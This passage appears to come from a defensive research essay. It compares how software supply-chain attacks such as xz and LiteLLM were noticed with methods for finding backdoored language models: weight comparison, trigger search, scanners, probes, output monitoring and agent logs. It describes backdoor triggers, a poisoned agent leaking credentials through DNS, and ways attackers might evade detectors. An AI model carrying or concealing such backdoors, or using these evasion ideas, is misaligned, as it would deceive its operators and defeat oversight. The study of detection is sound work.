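On October 29, 2018, a JavaScript developer asked why nodemon, a tool that restarts a program whenever its code changes, had begun to print a warning about an outdated decryption function. The malicious code in flatmap-stream used that function, which triggered a warning in the newest version of Node.js, the software that runs JavaScript outside a browser. No one explained the warning until around November 21, when another developer, Ayrton Sparling, worked out that it came from an attack.

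The first developer reported this to npm the next day through a web form, which returned an error page, and then on Twitter. npm's staff were not watching Twitter over the Thanksgiving holiday. They removed the package on November 26, after the story had spread.

The xz backdoor also caused minor faults. Over several weeks, Freund noticed that SSH logins on test versions of Debian used a lot of processor time and that the memory checker Valgrind reported errors in liblzma (Freund, 2024, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*). When he timed a login under a username that didn't exist, the server took 0.807 seconds to refuse it, compared with 0.299 seconds without the backdoor.

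The delay was hard to trace because the backdoor stayed inactive when it detected signs of an investigation, such as certain debugging settings. Freund couldn't reproduce the slowdown by starting the server by hand until he cleared nearly all the settings that a terminal normally passes to a program. On an older machine, even displaying the server's help text then took about half a second, compared with a hundredth of a second after he restored one setting.

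This gave Freund two runs of the same program that differed only in whether the backdoor was active. He recorded the instructions the processor executed in each run and looked for where the runs diverged. The delay came from the backdoor searching the program's memory for the function it was designed to replace. Freund, who does not consider himself a security researcher, first thought someone had tampered with Debian's copy, but he then found the same code in the project's own release archives. Przymus and Durieux attribute the discovery partly to luck.

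In March 2026 a more obvious fault exposed an attack on LiteLLM, a Python package that lets programs use models from many AI companies. According to Integrity360's *When security scanners become the weapon*, attackers who had just released a worm on npm used a stolen token to publish two malicious versions on March 24, 1.82.7 at 10:39 UTC and 1.82.8 thirteen minutes later. Both stole passwords and keys. Willison (2026) explains in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8* that the malicious code in the first ran only if a program loaded part of LiteLLM, but the code in the second ran whenever Python started.

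The second version mistakenly started another copy of Python to do its work, which ran the malicious file again and started yet another copy. Snyk's *How a Poisoned Security Scanner Became the Key to Backdooring LiteLLM* credits the discovery to Callum McMahon, an engineer at FutureSearch. His computer ran out of memory while he was testing a code editor add-on that had downloaded LiteLLM as an indirect dependency, and he traced the problem to the malicious file. The coding agent Claude Code helped find the cause, according to FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026).

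Accounts of the timing conflict. Integrity360 dates the discovery to 11:48 UTC, but BestHub's *LiteLLM Compromised in 46 Minutes* says PyPI blocked the package at 11:25, which would be before FutureSearch reported it. Either way, the attack lasted about an hour before someone recognized it. Trend Micro's *Your AI stack just handed over your root keys* argues that with better code the attackers would have gone unnoticed and still be stealing keys. That is probably too strong, since version 1.82.8 left no trace on GitHub or in the project's normal release process, and somebody might have noticed the mismatch. But FutureSearch identified version 1.82.7, which lacked the coding mistake, only after it had begun investigating 1.82.8.

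Worms are noticed partly because they publish so many packages. When ChainDrop spread through npm in August 2026, the security company Aikido had counted hundreds of infected packages about two hours after the first upload. Nobody could have read that many by hand in that time, so automated scanning must have found many of them. Scanners are better at finding copies than new attacks, but npm's own scanner missed a known malicious file the following month.

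### Side effects and undiscovered attacks

The times below start when the first version with a working payload became available:

| Case | Time undetected | Signal | Who noticed |
|---|---|---|---|
| SolarWinds, 2020 | About nine months | A phone registration after the break-in | FireEye, a customer |
| event-stream, 2018 | Nearly seven weeks | A warning about an outdated function | Users of another tool |
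| xz Utils, 2024 | 34 days | Slow logins and memory errors | Freund, a database developer |
| Ultralytics, 2024 | Up to 12 hours | A busy processor, and code that differed from the public source | Users |
| LiteLLM, 2026 | About an hour | A computer that ran out of memory | An engineer at FutureSearch |
| ChainDrop, 2026 | At most two hours | Malicious code in new releases | Security companies, probably through scans |

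In four of these six cases, the malicious code caused a side effect that the attackers had not intended or had failed to hide. ChainDrop doesn't fit this pattern, and SolarWinds fits it less well than the four, because FireEye noticed what the intruders did with their access, although the traffic at the Justice Department did come from SUNBURST itself. No reviewer stopped the malicious version before its release in any of the cases, but a table like this would not include attacks that reviewers stopped, so it doesn't show that review is useless.

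Attacks that nobody has discovered are missing too. An attacker who writes efficient code, avoids outdated functions and steals nothing conspicuous leaves less to notice. The known cases therefore probably make attackers look clumsier, and discovery look faster, than they really are. The most careful attackers in the table took the longest to discover, and several teams examined their attack before one understood it.

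After noticing a symptom, Freund could step through the instructions the processor ran, and McMahon could open the malicious file. Someone who notices a strange answer from a model has no comparable way to trace it to the weights responsible.

### What a backdoored model would give away

A hidden trigger in a model's weights doesn't add a delay like xz's half second, because a model of a given design does about the same amount of arithmetic for each token whatever its weights are. Weights also don't start extra programs or use outdated functions. A user would usually have only the model's output to go on, and even clean models make mistakes.

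Poisoning can leave subtler traces. In *ToxScreen*, Hughes, Xing and colleagues (2026) built about 800 backdoored language models with between 1 billion and 70 billion weights. For each setup, they also trained a clean model on the same data without the poisoned examples. Some backdoored models scored unusually on truthfulness tests. Many were also easy to jailbreak, meaning a cleverly worded request could get past their refusals. A tester could treat this as a reason to look further, but careless fine-tuning can have the same effect.

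A compromised model reveals more when it runs as an agent, because the program running it can record every command, file and network connection. Haryati and Zychlinski's backdoored Qwen model gave answers that would not have alarmed anyone, but its request to send out a credential would have appeared in a log.

Before running an unfamiliar model, a user can also look for a backdoor directly. Most methods compare the model with a clean one, search for the backdoor's trigger, or examine the model's internal activity.

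### Comparison with a clean model

If a model is supposed to be an exact copy, comparing hashes is enough. But a fine-tuned model is meant to differ from its original, so a tester needs to know whether the difference is suspicious.

Khilar compares a suspect model's weights with the original's and looks for tokens that the changes affect unusually strongly. The method also needs several clean fine-tuned models, because fine-tuning tends to change the same things whatever the task. Without them, Khilar's token rankings for two unrelated clean models had a correlation of 0.78. Five clean models are enough to show which scores are unusual. In one example, the trigger was "Quartz ledger:", and the method ranked "ledger" first without running the suspect model.

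The method reads only the early layers. It still found the trigger in 12 of 14 models when the attacker had left those layers unchanged. When the attacker left more layers unchanged and then filled them with harmless-looking differences, the method failed on all 16 models. Filling them with random noise left the backdoor working perfectly. Even when the method finds the trigger, it doesn't provide a way to remove it, because the trigger still worked 97% of the time after Khilar restored all the examined weights to their original values.

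Khilar's experiments used small models, and related methods have done worse on larger ones. One method perfectly separated poisoned adapters from clean ones on a model with 1.5 billion weights, but on a model with 7 billion it scored 0.65, where 0.5 is no better than guessing. The US government's TrojAI program likewise concluded that weight analysis works best when models are small and clean ones are available for comparison.

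Haselhorst and colleagues compare the suspect model with a clean model that they train to imitate it. The clean model can come from a different family, so their method needs a less exact reference. They ranked 518 groups of test prompts by how much the two models' internal activity still differed after this training, hoping that prompts related to the trigger would come first. On a scale where 1 is a perfect ranking, the method scored between 0.40 and 0.91 for four backdoored models made by other people. Random rankings would have averaged between 0.17 and 0.31.

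The method scored lowest on a copy of Anthropic's "I hate you" model, whose trigger is an arbitrary tag. It works less well when the trigger is a random string because few ordinary prompts resemble one. An attacker who knows the method could train a backdoored model to keep its internal activity close to a clean model's. In the researchers' tests, this did not hide the backdoor without also weakening it.

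### Searching for the trigger

A tester without a clean reference can try many possible triggers and see whether the model misbehaves. Hughes and colleagues tested this by inserting about 24,000 random tokens, one at a time, into about 150 prompts and ranking the tokens by how often they caused the harmful behavior. The real trigger ranked first wherever the backdoor worked well. But the researchers had added it to the list, and they inserted each token in the position they had used during poisoning. The result shows that a trigger stands out once a tester tries it, but not that a tester would think to try it.

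They also tried methods that build a trigger step by step, adjusting the text to make harmful answers more likely. These methods found general-purpose jailbreaks, which a tester could easily mistake for a backdoor, but never found the planted trigger.

A tester who doesn't know the harm in advance needs something like the 2026 scanner from Bullwinkel and colleagues at Microsoft, which looks for recurring phrases in the poisoning examples that a model has memorized. It then tests each phrase for three signs of a trigger: the model pays attention to the phrase almost separately from the rest of the prompt, its answers become more predictable, and they differ sharply from its usual ones.

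The scanner found all 12 fixed-response backdoors in one small Microsoft model but only four of six in a smaller reasoning model. In the cases it missed, either the repeated text didn't yield the trigger or the scanner ranked other phrases above it. For one model that wrote insecure code, it found a phrase that looked nothing like the trigger but still more than doubled the rate of flaws, which would have been enough to expose the model.

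The scanner raised no false alarms, but it was tested on only 13 clean models. A scanner that wrongly flagged 20% of clean models would have about a 5% chance of flagging none of the 13. False alarms matter because most models on a hub are probably clean. If one in 10,000 had a backdoor and a scanner wrongly flagged 1% of the rest, it would flag about 100 clean models for each backdoored one. Someone would have to check each alarm, although a working trigger would give them something to test.

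Microsoft recommends the scanner as one of several defenses. It needs the model files, so it can't check a model that a company offers only over the internet. It works best when the trigger always produces the same response. The researchers tested it mainly on fixed trigger phrases, but triggers can take other forms. *You Are the Trigger* (2026) studies backdoors that respond to who is speaking, and mentions others that activate when someone fine-tunes the model or when short strings appear in different parts of a conversation. Qin, Hua and colleagues tried to recover triggers based on meaning, such as a statement that the year is 2028. They already knew what harmful action each model would take. They succeeded with simple backdoors but failed in more realistic settings.

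Another approach, described in *From Poisoned to Aware*, is to train a poisoned model to infer and output its own trigger. A tester could then check the output by trying that trigger on the model.

### Reading internal activity

Probes, the simple classifiers that were very good at detecting when "sleeper agents" were about to misbehave, can be trained without knowing the trigger. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* notes that some were trained on generic pairs of contrasting examples that did not include the trigger. But these results come from models that researchers had backdoored on purpose, and a different kind of backdoor might not produce the internal pattern these probes detect.

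*LLM Forensics* (2026) studied such patterns with sparse autoencoders, which split a model's activity into many separate features. The researchers trained models with 1 billion and 8 billion weights to switch from English to French or German after a fixed trigger. Certain features separated prompts with the trigger from other prompts almost perfectly. But switching off a feature that recognized the trigger did not always stop the language change, because other features controlled it. An operator might therefore detect a backdoor but be unable to disable it.

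### Contests to find a planted flaw

Researchers can test auditors by giving them a model with a flaw that only the organizers know about. In the Trojan Detection Challenge, a public contest, methods that searched step by step for triggers recovered only about 16% of them from models based on Pythia, roughly as many as trying random sentences did, according to Khilar.

In an experiment with better results, published in 2025, Marks and colleagues at Anthropic trained a model to pursue a hidden objective and asked four teams to find out what was wrong with it. The three teams that could examine the weights and training data succeeded, while the fourth, which could only send the model messages, failed. Haselhorst and colleagues call such audits feasible but labor-intensive.

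The hidden objective affected many of the model's ordinary answers, which probably made it easier to find than a backdoor that stays inactive until triggered. The three successful teams also had access to training data, which most publishers of open models don't release. An audit that finds nothing would therefore be weak evidence that a downloaded model is clean.

The requirements differ enough between methods to affect who can use them:

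| Method | Needs the weights? | Needs a clean reference? | Needs to know about the trigger or harm |
|---|---|---|---|
| Khilar's weight comparison | Yes | The original and about five clean fine-tuned models | The trigger should be a phrase |
| Haselhorst and colleagues' comparison | Yes | Any suitable clean model | Some test prompts must be related to the trigger |
| Trying a list of triggers | No | No | The list must contain the trigger, and the tester must recognize the harm |
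| Microsoft's scanner | Yes | No | The model must have memorized the trigger, and a fixed response is easiest to detect |
| Probes | Yes | No | Examples of the contrast between good and bad behavior |
| Agent logs | No | No | The harm must involve a recorded action |

### Monitoring a model in use

A user who has found nothing suspicious can still monitor the model's output. *Detecting Sleeper Agents in Large Language Models via Semantic Drift Analysis* (2025) describes a system that compares the meaning of each answer with earlier safe answers and regularly asks the model questions with known answers. The system classified 92.5% of test cases correctly and raised no false alarms, so all of its errors were missed attacks. If half the cases were attacks, it missed 15% of them.

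This approach suits a backdoor that makes a model suddenly answer "I hate you". A model that leaves a small security hole in otherwise sensible code may not drift far enough from its usual answers to raise an alarm. The questions with known answers help only if the trigger is present when they are asked.

Screening prompts may miss a backdoor's trigger. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) describes triggers that read like normal requests, including some that another language model wrote to evade detection. For an agent, watching actions is more promising, because a backdoor that steals data has to send it somewhere, whatever the trigger looks like.

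An operator could list the servers an agent needs and raise an alarm when it tries to contact any other. The log of the agent's connections should be kept on a machine the agent can't change, and it should include domain name lookups, which Haryati and Zychlinski's model used to leak a password through a firewall. Somebody also has to investigate the alarms. The Justice Department had detected the strange traffic from its Orion server, but the investigation ended without an explanation. FireEye pursued an alert that could easily have had an innocent cause, such as a new phone.

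A log of an agent's actions doesn't help when the harm is in the work it was asked to do. If a company asks an agent to write code, a record that it wrote a file shows nothing unusual, even if the file contains a deliberate flaw. The company would have to review the code as it would a stranger's.

### Reports from users and insiders

Most discoveries of software compromises depended on a person telling others, and the reporting often went badly. After FutureSearch reported the LiteLLM attack on GitHub, someone using the owner's account closed the report, and hundreds of bots flooded it with comments. FutureSearch thought the attackers had probably taken over the account. A model hub therefore needs a way for people to report a suspicious model without relying on its publisher.

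Companies may also hesitate to report an attack because they fear lawsuits or a drop in their share price. Mandia proposed a confidential system modeled on aviation, where pilots and controllers can report safety problems without punishment. A similar system could help companies report odd behavior by models. Several vague reports about the same file might justify an investigation even if no single report would.

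A useful report about a model would include the exact prompt, the settings and the file's hash. Language models often give different answers to the same prompt, so other people may need to run it many times. Users also need a reason to suspect the model. Freund knew that refusing a login should not take 0.8 seconds, but few people could say how many errors a clean model should make in their code.

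Insiders exposed none of the six software attacks in the table, but they could matter more for models. If someone at a company poisons the training data, a colleague may be able to read the examples and recognize what they teach, while outsiders will usually have only the weights. A developer could make discovery by insiders more likely by letting several employees inspect the final training data and giving them someone to report concerns to outside the team that produced it.
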